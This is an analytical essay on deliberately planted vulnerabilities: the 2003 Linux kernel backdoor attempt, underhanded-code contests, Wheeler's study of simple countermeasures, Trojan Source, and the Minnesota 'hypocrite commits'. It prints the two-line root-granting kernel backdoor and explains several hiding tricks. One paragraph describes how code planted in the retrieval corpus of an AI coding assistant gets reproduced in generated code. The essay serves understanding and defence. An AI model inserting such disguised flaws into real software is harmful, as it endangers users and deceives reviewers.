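# Why subtly vulnerable code slips past human reviewers and static analyzers

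## How code is checked, and a one-character attack on Linux in 2003

Before programmers trust new code, colleagues read it, automatic tools scan it for known kinds of mistakes, tests run it, and a record-keeping system logs who wrote it and who accepted it. Code can pass all these checks and still contain a vulnerability, a defect that lets someone do what the program's owner meant to forbid, such as reading private files or taking over the machine. Most vulnerabilities start as unnoticed mistakes, called bugs, but occasionally someone writes one on purpose and makes it look like working code. In November 2003, someone tried this on the Linux kernel, the part of the Linux operating system that controls what every other program on a computer may do.

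At that time the kernel's developers kept the master copy of their source code in BitKeeper, a version-control system: a program that stores a project's code together with the history of its changes. A single recorded change is a commit. BitKeeper was a commercial product and some developers would not use it, so BitMover, the company behind it, also offered the code through an older, free system, CVS. The CVS copy was an outlet only, as Corbet (2003), in *An attempt to backdoor the kernel*, explains. BitMover generated it from BitKeeper, and nobody was supposed to commit new work there. An intruder got onto the server that held this copy and added two lines to one file, under the name of David Miller, an established kernel developer:

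```
if ((options == (__WCLONE|__WALL)) && (current->uid = 0))
        retval = -EINVAL;
```

The lines are in a routine called wait4, which a program uses to pause until another program has finished. On a quick reading, they look like an error check that rejects the call as invalid if the caller has passed two particular options together and is user number 0. The two options make no sense together, so the check seems fine, "if somewhat strangely specific" (Markham, 2003, *Comments on "An attempt to backdoor the kernel"*).

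The attack depends on a missing equals sign. In C, the programming language of the kernel, `x == 0` tests whether x is zero and leaves x unchanged, while `x = 0` sets x to zero. C allows an assignment inside a condition, so the line is legal. It sets the user's number to 0 instead of checking whether it is 0. On Linux, that number belongs to root, the administrator's account, which can read, change or delete anything.

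Two rules of C also helped hide the effect. C evaluates the second half of such a condition only if the first half is true, so the assignment did not run during normal calls to wait4, and an ordinary test of the kernel would have shown nothing wrong. When the assignment did run, it produced zero, which C treats as false. The condition therefore failed, the error line never ran, and the calling program carried on as root.

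A backdoor is a hidden way past a system's access controls, put there by someone who wants to use it later. Only someone who could already run a program on the machine could have used this one, though on a computer with many account holders that would still be many people. Corbet corrects the claim, reported at the time, that it allowed attacks over the network.

### How the change came to light

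A nightly job exposed the line, which nobody had found by reading the code. Larry McVoy, the head of BitMover, describes the job in *BK2CVS problem* (McVoy, 2003), a thread on the kernel developers' mailing list. Each night, his company exported the kernel code from BitKeeper to a CVS copy on its own machine, sent the updated files to the public server, then computed checksums on both machines and compared them. A checksum is a short number that a program derives from the whole contents of a file; if one character changes, the number almost certainly changes too. On 5 November, the checksums for one file did not match.

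McVoy then looked at that file's history. Genuine entries ended with a pointer to the BitKeeper change they came from. The three newest entries had no pointer, so they had not come through BitKeeper, and Miller denied having made them. *The Linux Backdoor Attempt of 2003*, a blog post from Princeton's Center for Information Technology Policy, describes the pointer as leading to the record of a change's approval, and implies that the missing pointer led to the discovery. In McVoy's own account, the checksums came first. In both versions, the intruder was caught because of the code's provenance, the record of who wrote it, who approved it and how it reached its present place. The nightly comparison would have flagged any change made outside BitKeeper, even a corrected spelling in a comment.

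Accounts differ on how quickly the change was discovered. Route Fifty's *Effort to compromise Linux kernel foiled* (2003) puts the change at about 2 a.m. on 5 November and its discovery about four hours later. The entries in the file's history are dated 4 November, and McVoy told the list only that BitMover had found and fixed the problem in less than 24 hours.

In his first message, McVoy called the incident "not a big deal" and did not mention a backdoor. When a member of the list asked what the changed lines were, McVoy posted the diff, which shows the lines that a change adds or removes and a few unchanged lines around them. Ten minutes later a reader answered that it looked odd. Fifteen minutes after that, another reader, Chad Kitching, pointed out that the code set the user number to zero and asked whether it was an attempt at a backdoor. McVoy replied, "Good eyes, I missed that."

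So a specialist who already knew that the two lines were illegitimate looked at them and missed what they did. Others saw it quickly, but they also knew that the lines had arrived by an irregular route, and they had only two lines to read. A reviewer doing routine work usually has neither advantage.

### Whether a reviewer would have caught it

In code review, someone other than the author reads a proposed change before the project accepts it. In an open-source project such as Linux, anyone may read the code and propose changes, and maintainers decide whether to accept them. Linus Torvalds, who created Linux and leads its development, wrote in the same thread that changes reached him as patches by email or through BitKeeper. An emailed patch got more or less scrutiny depending on the sender, but a change to a core file "would definitely get a read-through and need an explanation".

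The intruder bypassed these checks, so the case doesn't directly test review. Opinions varied on whether reviewers would have caught the change. In *Thwarted Linux backdoor hints at smarter hacks* (Poulsen, 2003), the security consultant Ryan Russell called the line "indistinguishable from an accidental bug" and said nobody would investigate it without a reason for suspicion. Torvalds's demand for an explanation might have worked better than the read-through. Kitching had noticed that the next line of the file overwrote the error code, so the supposed check would have achieved nothing even with the right number of equals signs. A reviewer who asked only whether the two lines looked right could easily have let them pass, but asking what they were for would have turned up no good answer.

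McVoy told reporters that somebody else would have caught the change if BitMover had not, since so many people use and read the code. Two days later, a commenter under Corbet's article credited the many eyes of open source with the discovery. McVoy, signing as lm (2003), called this nonsense in *One attempt thwarted*. He wrote that hundreds of people could have detected the change, and asked why they hadn't. The two statements can both be true, because the first is about what would have happened eventually, and a day is not much time to notice two lines in a project the size of the kernel. Still, the only actual detection came from an automatic comparison and BitMover's habit of distrust.

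### What an automatic tool would have reported

A static analyzer is a program that looks for flaws in code without running it. A C compiler, which translates source code into instructions for the machine, also works as a simple static analyzer, because it prints warnings about suspicious code. The GNU compiler, gcc, has a warning for this slip, a single equals sign where a condition needs a true-or-false answer. But programmers sometimes assign a value inside a condition on purpose, so gcc treats brackets around the assignment as a sign that it is intentional. The 2003 line has those brackets, so gcc would not have warned about it. This would have been a false negative, a flaw that a check misses.

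A stricter rule would have caught the line. In the comments on Corbet's article, one reader suggested a warning whenever part of a condition has a fixed value, as an assignment of zero always does. Another pointed out that this rule would also produce false positives, warnings about code that has no flaw, for example where a project switches off an optional feature by defining its name as zero. Programmers stop reading warnings when too many are false, so whoever sets an analyzer's rules has to decide how many false positives to accept. Rules that avoid flagging common, harmless code will tend to miss flaws that resemble it.

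Other analyzers do more than match suspicious phrases, and some trace data through a program from where an outsider can supply it to where it can do harm. Simple countermeasures may also help a good deal. In *Initial Analysis of Underhanded Source Code*, a study for the Institute for Defense Analyses in the United States, Wheeler (2020) recommends trying simple countermeasures such as compiler warnings and better display of code against attacks of this type, and tests some of them on entries to a programming contest.

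### Planted or accidental

Wheeler counts the 2003 line as underhanded code, which is readable source code deliberately written to do something other than what it appears to do. Intent is hard to prove from the code, because typing one equals sign instead of two is among the oldest mistakes in C. In *Attempted attack on Linux kernel foiled* (Lemos, 2003), McVoy says that a Trojan horse (a harmful function inside an innocent-looking program) is just a bug that somebody has put in deliberately.

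Security researchers had drawn this distinction well before. Landwehr, Bull and colleagues (1994), in *A Taxonomy of Computer Program Security Flaws, with Examples*, documented 50 actual flaws and proposed a scheme for sorting them, in part by genesis, or how the flaw got into the system. As *A Software Flaw Taxonomy* summarizes it, the scheme separates intentional flaws from inadvertent (accidental) ones, then divides the intentional ones into malicious insertions and unintended consequences of a design decision. Malicious insertions are planted flaws, meaning vulnerabilities that somebody put into code on purpose.

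The most convincing evidence that the 2003 flaw was planted is that somebody had broken into a server to insert the line under another person's name. Nobody has publicly identified the intruder. There is also evidence in the code itself. Markham thought the brackets were strictly unnecessary and inferred that the attacker had known how to silence the compiler. A reader of the Princeton CITP post weakened this argument by noting that the line would not compile without the brackets, and that many programmers put brackets around genuine comparisons out of habit. InfoQ's *Linux Backdoor* (2013) makes the better argument that a routine for waiting has no reason to deal with the user's identity. McVoy told Poulsen that whoever wrote the line must have searched for options that cause no error but never normally occur together.

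A planted flaw can be identical to an accidental one, so a tool that sees only the code cannot always distinguish them. But an attacker can test a planted flaw against the compiler first and keep a version that draws no warning. A check may therefore be less effective against planted flaws than its record against accidental ones suggests.

### What provenance could not have settled

The people involved disagreed on how close the line came to a real release. Torvalds saw no way for it to get there, because the developers who merged work through BitKeeper did not use the CVS copy. Corbet agreed that the main kernel was never at risk. McVoy thought that a developer working from CVS could have sent in a patch containing the line. Another commenter observed that a CVS user who prepares a patch in the normal way sends only his own changes, not those that other people have made to the shared copy.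 McVoy's scenario therefore required a careless developer and then an inattentive maintainer. Theodore Ts'o, another kernel developer, raised a different risk, that a Linux distributor might have built its product from the CVS copy, though none is known to have done so. INCIBE's *CVE-2003-1161* (2003), an entry in the public list of vulnerabilities, rates the severity of the flaw as high, at 7.2, while CNCF's *Linux Kernel CVS Repository Hack* rates the impact of the incident as low, because the altered copy was only a mirror.

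Ts'o worried more about changes submitted through the normal process. A small patch that claimed to fix a bug but opened a security hole might get past Torvalds if it seemed to come from a trusted developer. Ts'o had long wanted BitKeeper to attach a digital signature to every change, a cryptographic mark that lets anyone verify who made it, and McVoy now promised to add one. Signatures would stop an impostor, but neither they nor BitMover's nightly comparison would stop a bad change from a contributor who signs with his own name. Once a maintainer had accepted such a change, both copies would contain it, the checksums would agree, and the pointer would lead to a genuine approval.

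AI coding assistants add another route by which code reaches a project. These assistants use a language model to write code on request, and many first search a stored collection of code and documents, called the retrieval corpus, for the few entries that best match the request. The model receives these entries along with the request, and often imitates their structure and calls the same functions. This technique, called retrieval-augmented code generation, is useful for material the model's training did not cover, such as a company's private libraries or an interface that has changed since. But the search typically ranks entries by how closely they resemble the request, and an unsafe example can resemble it as closely as a safe one. If somebody plants a flaw in an entry, making it a poisoned example, the model may repeat the flaw for every developer whose request retrieves that entry. The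 new code then enters the project under the developer's name, and unless the assistant records what it retrieved, a reviewer has nothing linking the code to the poisoned example.

BitMover's comparison caught the 2003 line without analyzing what it did, while McVoy read the line and didn't notice the problem. Any check on code, whether in a kernel or a retrieval corpus, misses problems that don't show up in what it examines.

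## Underhanded-code contests and how many entries simple checks catch

Whoever tried to compromise the Linux kernel in 2003 left two lines of code and no explanation. Programming contests have since provided much more material to study. Entrants openly write underhanded code for small prizes, and the organizers publish explanations of how the best entries deceive a reader.

The earliest such contest that Wheeler found was Obfuscated V, which Daniel Horn ran during the 2004 US presidential election. *The Obfuscated V contest* (Horn, 2004) asked for a program that appeared to count votes correctly but favoured one candidate, either always or only on election day, 2 November. Programs that miscounted only on election day had to count correctly in a trial run on 1 November. Judges then read the entries and ran the one that looked most correct, which won if it miscounted.

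Scott Craver, a computer security researcher at Binghamton University, took up the idea a year later, according to *International contest asks hackers to write 'evil' code* (2015). His Underhanded C Contest ran from 2005 to 2009 and again from 2013 to 2015, with a new task each time. Other contests followed for particular fields and languages: the Underhanded Crypto Contest (2014 to 2018), the JavaScript Misdirection Contest (2015), and a 2017 contest for Solidity, a language for programs that hold and move money on a blockchain. Wheeler found no published winners or samples from another contest announced for Rust.

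### What earned points

Craver's contest gave more points to short, readable code, because a flaw is harder to hide in a few clear lines. *The 2009 challenge*, from the Underhanded C Contest, lists two further criteria. Most programmers use editors that show comments, numbers and commands in different colours, and an entry earned more points if this syntax colouring did not reveal the flaw. It also earned more if the flaw, once discovered, was "plausibly deniable as a newbie coding mistake".

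*Results of the 2015 Underhanded C Contest* (Craver, 2016) reprints the contest's rules, under which errors that exploit human eyesight counted as much as errors that exploit obscure rules of C. The contest also rewarded triggers that an attacker could easily arrange but that would rarely occur by accident. A flaw with such a trigger will usually survive testing, as the 2003 line would have.

Contest judges, unlike ordinary reviewers, know that every entry contains a flaw, but they can still miss it. The 2014 task was to write surveillance code for a service like Twitter that would secretly let users find out they were being watched. In *2014 Winners* (2015), Craver admits to staring for some time at one very short, readable entry without finding the bug. The code he was reading contained no error. The flaw was in a routine that the entrant had left out and only described in a comment. That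 routine would fetch the user's profile picture from whatever web address the user had supplied, so a user who controlled the address would see the visit.

### Two winning programs

The 2008 task was to write a program that blacks out rectangles in an image, as an office might to hide names in a scanned document, but leaves some of the hidden content recoverable. The contest drew more than 100 entries. John Meacham won with a 55-line program that blacked out the rectangles in about the most obvious way possible.

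His program used an image format that stores the brightness of each point as ordinary decimal digits. Inside the rectangle, the program replaced every digit with a zero, so a dark point with a one-digit value became 0 and a bright point with a three-digit value became 000. Image software reads both as zero and displays black, but the file still contains the original number of digits for each value, which is enough to tell dark ink from white paper.

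Anyone who viewed the program's output image would have seen a solid black box, and a test that compared the numerical values would have found only zeros. A static analyzer would have had little to report because the program performs no dangerous operation. To notice the problem, a reviewer has to ask what blacking out is supposed to achieve and then look at the stored file instead of the picture.

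The 2015 task came from nuclear disarmament. Inspectors can check that a warhead is genuine by measuring its gamma rays, which form a pattern of peaks characteristic of the material inside. The full measurement would reveal secrets of the weapon's design, so the task called for a program that compares it with a reference pattern and reports only yes or no. Entrants had to write the comparison so that the country being inspected could get a false yes. The contest was sponsored by the Nuclear Threat Initiative, a nonprofit that works to reduce the threat of weapons of mass destruction. Its *"Underhanded C" Contest Highlights Challenges For Nuclear Arms Control Verification Technologies* notes that no standards existed for writing or reviewing this kind of code.

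Linus Åkesson won with a program that uses two different sizes for the same type of number. A shared definitions file makes this type eight bytes long. The file that carries out the final comparison should include these definitions but doesn't, so it takes the type from C's standard mathematics library, where it is normally four bytes long. The comparison therefore reads a list of eight-byte numbers as a list of four-byte numbers.

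As Åkesson explains, the program then compares only the first half of the measurement, and the misreading flattens the differences in height between peaks. A fake warhead could pass with a fraction of the real material, plus another radioactive substance whose peaks fall in the ignored half. He simulated 1,000 crude fakes, each with 10 percent of the genuine material, and a large proportion failed to fool the program. An inspector who tested it with arbitrary fakes would therefore often see it give the right answer, but a cheating country could pick the best fakes.

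Each file looks correct by itself. A C compiler normally processes one file at a time, so it finds no contradiction to warn about. A reviewer would have to notice that a line is missing. Craver wrote that if a reader misses the confusion of types, nothing in the rest of the program, some 60 lines in all, looks the slightest bit suspicious.

### Comments that reassure the reader

Comments are notes for human readers. The compiler ignores them, so a false comment causes no error. In the JavaScript contest, which received 34 valid entries, several entrants put a comment linking to Stack Overflow, a question-and-answer site for programmers, beside the harmful code. Wheeler quotes Peter Jaric, who announced the results, as calling this clever because reviewers are used to seeing such comments explain unusual code. Jaric also found it easier to skip over code with a good comment above it.

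One of the highest-scoring Obfuscated V entries used comments to justify an operation that had no legitimate purpose. Wheeler thought the comments were fairly effective at making it seem reasonable. A reviewer can guard against this by working out what the code does before reading the comments, but that takes longer, and comments are partly meant to save time.

Entrants also hid flaws in parts of a program that seem to exist for safety. The 2014 winner, Karen Pease, put hers in code that kept an audit record to prove compliance, and another entrant that year used a function for finding bugs. Craver's contest gave extra points for this kind of irony. This tactic may also work on real reviewers, who have more reason to scrutinize a program's main task than its record-keeping.

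### Wheeler's test of five countermeasures

Wheeler found no evidence that anyone had measured how well simple tools detect underhanded code, so he tried some on the Obfuscated V contest entries. Horn had published 41 entries, each with a short explanation of its trick, and two of them were Wheeler's own.

Even with the explanations, some of the faulty lines were hard to find, and four explanations were wrong, misleading or described attack code that was missing. One gave the cause of the miscount as a swap of the letter O and the digit zero, which was in the program but was not the cause. Another described a trick that depended on the compile command, which nobody had kept. A third used the word "gets", the name of a C function, probably to mean an equals sign. The fourth described an attack that was not in the program, which appeared to count correctly. Wheeler dropped that program, leaving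 40.

Of those 40, 25 relied on one of five familiar kinds of error. Wheeler then selected five countermeasures, partly to match these errors.

| Kind of error | Entries | Matching countermeasure | How Wheeler assessed it |
|---|---|---|---|
| Reading or writing outside the memory reserved for a value | 5 | A memory checker, which monitors the program as it runs | Predicted the result |
| Misuse of macros, which replace one piece of program text with another before compilation | 9 | Strict limits on macros | Judged from the code |
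| Look-alike characters, such as the letter l for the digit 1 | 7 | A ban on names that resemble numbers | Judged from the code |
| Working code disguised as a comment | 2 | Syntax colouring and automatic reformatting | Judged from the code |
| One equals sign where two belong | 2 | Warnings from the gcc compiler | Ran gcc |
| Other | 15 | Warnings from the gcc compiler | Ran gcc |

At least one countermeasure caught 30 of the 40 entries (75 percent): all 25 entries of familiar kinds and five others that gcc flagged. Gcc caught both entries with a missing equals sign because neither had the extra brackets used in the 2003 kernel attempt, which would have silenced the warning.

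A defect in gcc caused it to miss one more entry. Kristian Nielsen had indented his code so that a line inside a loop appeared to be outside it. The compiler has a warning for misleading indentation, but it did not appear, and Wheeler reported the defect to the developer. Wheeler concluded that anyone who relies on warnings for security should also test that they work.

That left nine entries. Wheeler judged that six of them, including one he wrote himself, would make a reviewer suspicious because of odd constructions or needless repetition. Only three, or 7.5 percent, were neither caught nor suspicious. In one, a loop reset only part of a table of values. Another converted stored numbers to the wrong type. The third was meant to accept a vote written as "n" or "N", but checked for "n" twice. Wheeler thought more compiler warnings could catch errors like these.

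The judges, who marked creativity and accuracy as well as believability, gave these three entries 5.3, 4.3 and 3.7 out of 10. The two winners scored 7.0 and 7.3, and gcc gave relevant warnings for both. A compiler can therefore easily catch a program that impresses human judges but miss an ordinary typing error.

### How far the result can be trusted

The 75 percent figure probably overstates how much new underhanded code the countermeasures would catch, because Wheeler chose them after studying the samples. He acknowledges that this could seem unfair, but his aim was only to show that a few simple measures can often work. Each familiar kind of error had its own countermeasure, so it isn't surprising that all 25 entries with those errors were caught.

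Wheeler also ran only one of the tools, gcc, on every entry. For lack of time, he predicted what the memory checker would report, and he judged what a tool for detecting look-alike characters would find if somebody built one. By a count of his table, gcc alone caught 15 of the 40 entries, including 12 of the 25 he considered unsuspicious to a human reader. The more solid finding is therefore that an ordinary compiler, with many warnings switched on, caught about half of the well-hidden entries.

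Even that result depends on the compiler being newer than the entries. Wheeler used gcc 7.5.0, whereas the contest's rules named versions from 2.95 to 3.4. The entrants couldn't have tested their programs against the newer version's warnings, but an attacker today could do so.

Wheeler did not measure false positives, because he applied the countermeasures only to rigged programs. Many entries triggered warnings about unrelated faults. He rightly didn't count these as detections, since a programmer could fix those faults and leave the planted flaw in place. Strict rules have a poor record on false positives. Wheeler cites Les Hatton, who tested MISRA C, a set of rules for critical software written in C, on real code in 2005 and found that far too few of the warnings pointed to real problems.

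Defenders of MISRA C reply that it was never meant to find bugs. Under its rules, a programmer may use a dangerous construction only if it is necessary and safe, and if the programmer can quickly convince a colleague of both. This requirement resembles Torvalds's demand that a change to a core kernel file come with an explanation.

Wheeler's figures overstate the attackers' strength in one respect. Nine of the 40 programs miscounted only on election day. The other 31 gave wrong totals in some cases on any date, and Wheeler notes that good tests could have exposed them. These 31 include the three that every other check missed. Testing would have been much less useful against later contest entries, because their flaws had to appear only under special conditions.

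Finally, all the samples came from one old contest, in C or C++, and most programs were small enough to read in one sitting. Wheeler recommended repeating the exercise with more samples. Solidity's developers have already used entries from a Solidity contest to improve their tools. Many entrants had reused the name of a built-in feature for something else. The developers had begun adding warnings about this shortly before the contest, and continued afterwards. Another common trick was to send money to a program without triggering its internal accounting, which the developers found harder to prevent by changing the language.

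### Flaws in the mathematics

Wheeler's countermeasures address how code is written. He did not examine the cryptography contest in detail, but observed that many winners had exploited highly technical weaknesses in the cryptographic methods themselves. *Underhanded Crypto* (ianG, 2014), a mailing-list post, quotes the contest's rules, which call for a system that "looks secure to experts" but has a subtle weakness.

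In 2014, the Underhanded Crypto Contest received 16 entries. Gaëtan Leurent, the runner-up, started from a published method for proving one's identity without revealing a secret. One step counts the ones in a number's binary form. Leurent supplied a supposedly better counting formula that returned zero for numbers with exactly 63 ones. Such numbers are so rare that the system worked almost all the time, but a person who knew about the exception could break it. Nothing in the code would trigger a compiler warning, and a programmer could confirm that the code follows the formula without realizing that the formula is wrong.

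The winning entry in a smaller contest the following year, described in Hornby's *Second Underhanded Crypto Contest*, also required specialist knowledge. Joseph Birr-Pixton made GnuPG, a widely used encryption program, leak the user's private key by exploiting how it chose a number for each digital signature. If that number isn't random enough, an outsider can work out the key from the signature. A reviewer who didn't know this might see only a harmless change to a technical detail.

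The contrast with the C contests has at least one exception. Meacham, who had won with the image program in 2008, also won the 2014 cryptography contest with a programming error. His code used one area of memory for two purposes, and a yes-or-no value of the wrong type caused it to process the wrong contents. Wheeler recommends having specialists review specialized code in depth. Simple tools can still help indirectly by dealing with the simpler tricks, which leaves those specialists more time for the mathematics.

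### When the screen shows a different program

Seven Obfuscated V entries relied on characters that look alike. Wheeler pointed out that the problem extends well beyond the letter l and the digit 1, because modern source files can use Unicode, which covers the world's writing systems. Unicode includes, for instance, a Greek capital letter that looks the same as the Latin A but is a different character. Wheeler suggested restricting source files to plain English characters where possible and allowing only a few invisible control characters, such as tabs and newlines.

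*Trojan Source* (2021), by Nicholas Boucher and Ross Anderson of the University of Cambridge, describes an attack that makes a reviewer see one program while the compiler builds another. Unicode has invisible control characters for mixing languages such as English with languages written from right to left, such as Arabic and Hebrew. These characters change the order in which a screen displays text, but the compiler still processes the text in its stored order. Reviewers can't find the attack by reading the displayed code, however carefully, though they could have seen the missing equals sign of 2003 that way.

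A program that examines the stored characters can easily detect text-direction controls. Rust's developers changed its compiler to reject them in comments and quoted text unless the programmer explicitly permits them. gcc's developers added a warning, and GitHub began showing a notice on affected files. Because people who write in Arabic or Hebrew have legitimate uses for these controls, gcc by default warns only about those that leave a change of direction unfinished.

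The fixes targeted control characters that reorder text, but Unicode also has characters that most editors don't visibly display. In October 2025, Koi Security reported a group of malicious code-editor add-ons, which it called GlassWorm. The add-ons stored harmful code in such characters, so the code looked like empty space to anyone who opened the file. A project can find these characters by scanning for anything outside an approved set, as Wheeler had proposed. But the scan must also cover the packaged add-on, because most users install it without opening its source.

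### Two constraints and an excuse

Wheeler argues more generally that underhanded code must do a specific wrong thing while looking as if it does the right thing. Each additional check rules out some of the programs that would meet both requirements, even if no check is reliable alone.

The 2015 contest offers some support. About a third of its more than 40 entries relied on a special value that C produces when a calculation has no valid result, such as zero divided by zero. Any ordinary comparison with this value counts as false, which could turn a rejection into an acceptance. Few of these entries reached the shortlist. Some needed contrived conditions, and others divided without first checking for zero, which an experienced C programmer notices at once. One entrant added a check that did not work, but this gave reviewers a second fault to find.

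Wheeler expects the risk of exposure to deter attackers, and he recommends keeping the details of some countermeasures secret so that nobody can prepare for all of them. Deterrence is weaker if discovery carries no penalty, so the contests rewarded plausible deniability. One runner-up in 2009 wrote a text-comparison function with redundant conditions and a single missing character. The organizers admired the redundancy because it misled the eye with a repeated pattern and made the author look like a beginner.

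An attacker who wants a vulnerability to look accidental has to imitate mistakes that honest programmers make, and compilers and analyzers have warnings for many of those. A more unusual error may avoid the warnings but is harder to pass off as an accident. Åkesson's program avoided the warnings and still looked accidental, because forgetting to include a file is an ordinary mistake and its effects appeared only when two files worked together. A reviewer who found such an error in a real project would naturally ask for a correction, and the contributor could apologize, fix it and submit something else.

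## The University of Minnesota "hypocrite commits"

In August 2020, researchers at the University of Minnesota used the invented name James Bond to email the Linux kernel developers a patch with a deliberate mistake. They wanted to find out whether maintainers would accept planted flaws. The patch was for a device driver, the code through which the kernel operates a piece of hardware. The driver's maintainer found the mistake and suggested a correct way to make the change. "Bond" admitted the patch was wrong and apologized for bothering the developers.

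Theodore Ts'o had worried in 2003 that such a patch might get past review. The Minnesota researchers tested this on the kernel without telling the maintainers. The episode produced two kinds of evidence that people often confuse. A few deceptive patches showed how maintainers respond to planted flaws. An audit of hundreds of older patches, which had been sent in good faith, showed how many honest mistakes the maintainers had accepted.

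### From false names to a ban

The researchers sent five patches between 4 and 21 August 2020, under the names James Bond and George Acosta. They later said that the earliest was a genuine fix, sent under Bond's name because they had already set up a computer for the experiment. *Report on University of Minnesota Breach-of-Trust Incident* (Mason, Rostedt and colleagues, 2021) supports their account, finding that someone in the group had previously attempted the same fix under a real name. Without that fix, the experiment consisted of four patches.

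The resulting paper, Wu and Lu's *On the Feasibility of Stealthily Introducing Vulnerabilities in Open-Source Software*, came out in November 2020. It uses the term "hypocrite commit" for a small patch that fixes a minor problem but creates a much more serious one. The IEEE Symposium on Security and Privacy, a leading academic conference, accepted the paper. Other researchers objected to the experiment as soon as they saw the abstract on Twitter.

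The kernel developers first responded collectively the following spring. On 6 April 2021, the Minnesota group sent five new patches, this time from a university address. Greg Kroah-Hartman, who maintains the kernel's stable releases, thought they fixed nothing. In a message quoted by Slashdot, he reminded the sender that the group had admitted to submitting patches it knew to be faulty, and asked what he was supposed to think of another obviously incorrect series. On 20 April he told developers to reject everything from the university, and the next day he began proposing to remove its earlier changes from the kernel. CNX Software's *PhD students willfully committed known malicious changes to mainline Linux* (2021) reported 190 proposed removals.

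In a statement forwarded to an Openwall security mailing list (2021), the heads of the university's computer science department promised to report their findings to the community. According to Mason and colleagues' timeline, the researchers published an apology on 24 April and withdrew the paper two days later. Mason and his co-authors made up the Technical Advisory Board of the Linux Foundation, a nonprofit that supports the kernel's development. They published their report, including the audit of older patches, on 5 May.

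Four days later, the University of Minnesota's *Statement from Computer Science & Engineering confirming Linux Technical Advisory Board findings* (2021) accepted the Board's account, apart from one missing email address. It called the experiment "ill-conceived" and confirmed that it had consisted of four patches, one of them valid. Kroah-Hartman had understandably but wrongly suspected the patches of April 2021, which came from a separate project and were sent in good faith, though they were of poor quality.

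### The last missing condition

Wu and Lu base their argument on the observation that a vulnerability usually needs several conditions, which may be in different parts of a program. When all but one are present, the program has what they call an "immature vulnerability". The program is not yet vulnerable, but a patch that supplies the last condition makes it so.

The paper's main example is the use-after-free. A program requests a piece of memory, works with it and then frees it so that other code can use the space. If part of the program keeps using the memory after that, it may read or overwrite whatever is there now, which an attacker can sometimes exploit. The flaw exists only when the program frees the memory and then uses it, so code that does only one of these is harmless.

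The last step can look harmless, as it did in an accidental case from the kernel's history. A patch added one line to the code that handles a failure to register a device. The line dropped the kernel's reference to the device, which is normal cleanup after an error. But this also caused the kernel to free a related piece of memory, which a different function then used and freed again. Wu and Lu report that the flaw stayed in the kernel for five years.

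A diff of that patch would have shown a sensible line with a few unchanged lines around it. To see the problem, a reviewer had to know about the side effect and the other function, neither of which the patch changed. Linus Åkesson's winning contest program of 2015 was similar, since each of its files looked correct by itself. Asking for an explanation might have exposed the kernel backdoor attempt of 2003, but it is less useful against a patch like this one, which has a good explanation because it does fix something.

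Before the patch, a static analyzer has no flaw to report. Afterwards, it has to connect lines in separate functions to find one, and Wu and Lu describe the tools that kernel developers used at the time as mostly matching patterns of simple bugs. Tests seldom run error-handling code, since something has to fail first. Testing drivers, which made up 62 percent of the kernel's code in 2020, normally requires the hardware.

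One remedy would be to repair immature vulnerabilities before anybody completes them. However, the rules for the kernel's stable releases require a patch to fix a real bug, and the developers told Wu and Lu that they would not accept preventive patches. One practical reason is the number of candidates. Wu and Lu's programs flagged more than 6,000 places in the kernel that could become use-after-free flaws, and they inspected only about 200 by hand before choosing three for their experiment. If most would never cause trouble, checking and patching them all would take a lot of time from maintainers who have little to spare.

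### What past patches showed

To find out how such flaws get through review, Wu and Lu collected 138 kernel vulnerabilities introduced by minor patches, meaning those that changed fewer than 30 lines and added no new function. All 138 were in the public list of vulnerabilities, and the researchers assumed that all were accidental. Minor patches introduced 9.8 percent of the listed kernel vulnerabilities whose origin and fix the researchers could trace.

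The researchers blamed most of the missed flaws on the complexity of the code, but blamed 9.4 percent on carelessness because those flaws were quite obvious. Inexperience does not explain the rest, because kernel maintainers wrote 37.3 percent of the patches that introduced vulnerabilities. Maintainers wrote a larger share, 47.8 percent, of a sample of 500 recent minor patches. Outsiders were therefore somewhat more likely to introduce vulnerabilities, but expert knowledge did not reliably prevent them.

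A separate comparison looked at use-after-free flaws from January 2015 to August 2020. The researchers gathered flaws that had reached the kernel and flaws that maintainers had blocked during review, and defined the catch rate as the share of the total that was blocked.

| What made the flaw hard to see | Catch rate |
|---|---|
| Several parts of the kernel running at the same time | 19.4% |
| A function that releases memory as a side effect | 36.3% |
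| Two names for the same piece of memory | 38.4% |
| A place in error-handling code | 42.0% |
| A call whose destination depends on the running program | 5 of 9 |
| Comparison group | 56.6% |

The pattern is plausible. Reviewers do worst when they have to imagine several sequences of events at once, and a diff helps little with that. The exact figures are less certain, because the paper gives the number of cases for only one category, which has nine. Five out of nine is about the same rate as in the comparison group, so it is no evidence that such calls hinder reviewers, but nine cases are too few to rule out a difference.

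Wu and Lu regard their catch rates as upper limits because some flaws that got past review are still undiscovered. That follows only if they found every flaw that maintainers blocked. A maintainer may reject a bad patch for another reason, such as poor style, and never mention the flaw. Counting any such cases they missed would raise the catch rate.

The researchers also measured how long flaws survived in the kernel. Flaws that depended on simultaneous activity again lasted longest. Those in error-handling code came second, although reviewers had caught them more often than the other two kinds measured. A likely reason is that error-handling code rarely runs, so tests and everyday use seldom expose its flaws. If a reviewer misses one, there may be no effective check after review.

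### What happened to the deceptive patches

The paper and the Board's report give incompatible accounts of the experiment. According to Wu and Lu, it consisted of three patches of fewer than five lines each. They wrote that whenever a maintainer said a patch looked good, they immediately pointed out the flaw, asked the maintainer not to apply the patch and supplied a correct one. They also wrote that maintainers had confirmed this in all three cases and that none of the faulty patches had become a commit. A reader of the paper would conclude that three planted flaws had passed review.

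Mason and colleagues traced four patches in the public email archive. A maintainer accepted one, which added an error message to a driver for encryption hardware, and it became a commit. The researchers had meant it to cause a use-after-free, but they misunderstood how the kernel manages such devices, and the patch contained no flaw. They asked about it after the maintainer had accepted it and learned that it was fine. Mason and colleagues could not explain why the paper still presented it as incorrect.

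Maintainers rejected the other three patches. One repeated a bad patch that someone had already submitted, and cited an automatic testing system as support. The first reply came after seven hours, and the maintainers quickly saw that the change was invalid and the sender's name was false. A reviewer replied to another patch, from "Acosta", in four and a half hours, explaining the error and suggesting how to correct it. "Acosta" never followed up, which contradicts the paper's claim that the researchers provided a proper fix every time. The last was the driver patch for which "Bond" apologized, and its maintainer took six days to reply.

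The Board had an interest in showing that kernel review works, but its account is better supported because it links to dated public messages and the university confirmed it after the authors had withdrawn their paper. However, the university also said that all four patches stopped at the review stage, but the valid one was in the kernel until the developers removed it.

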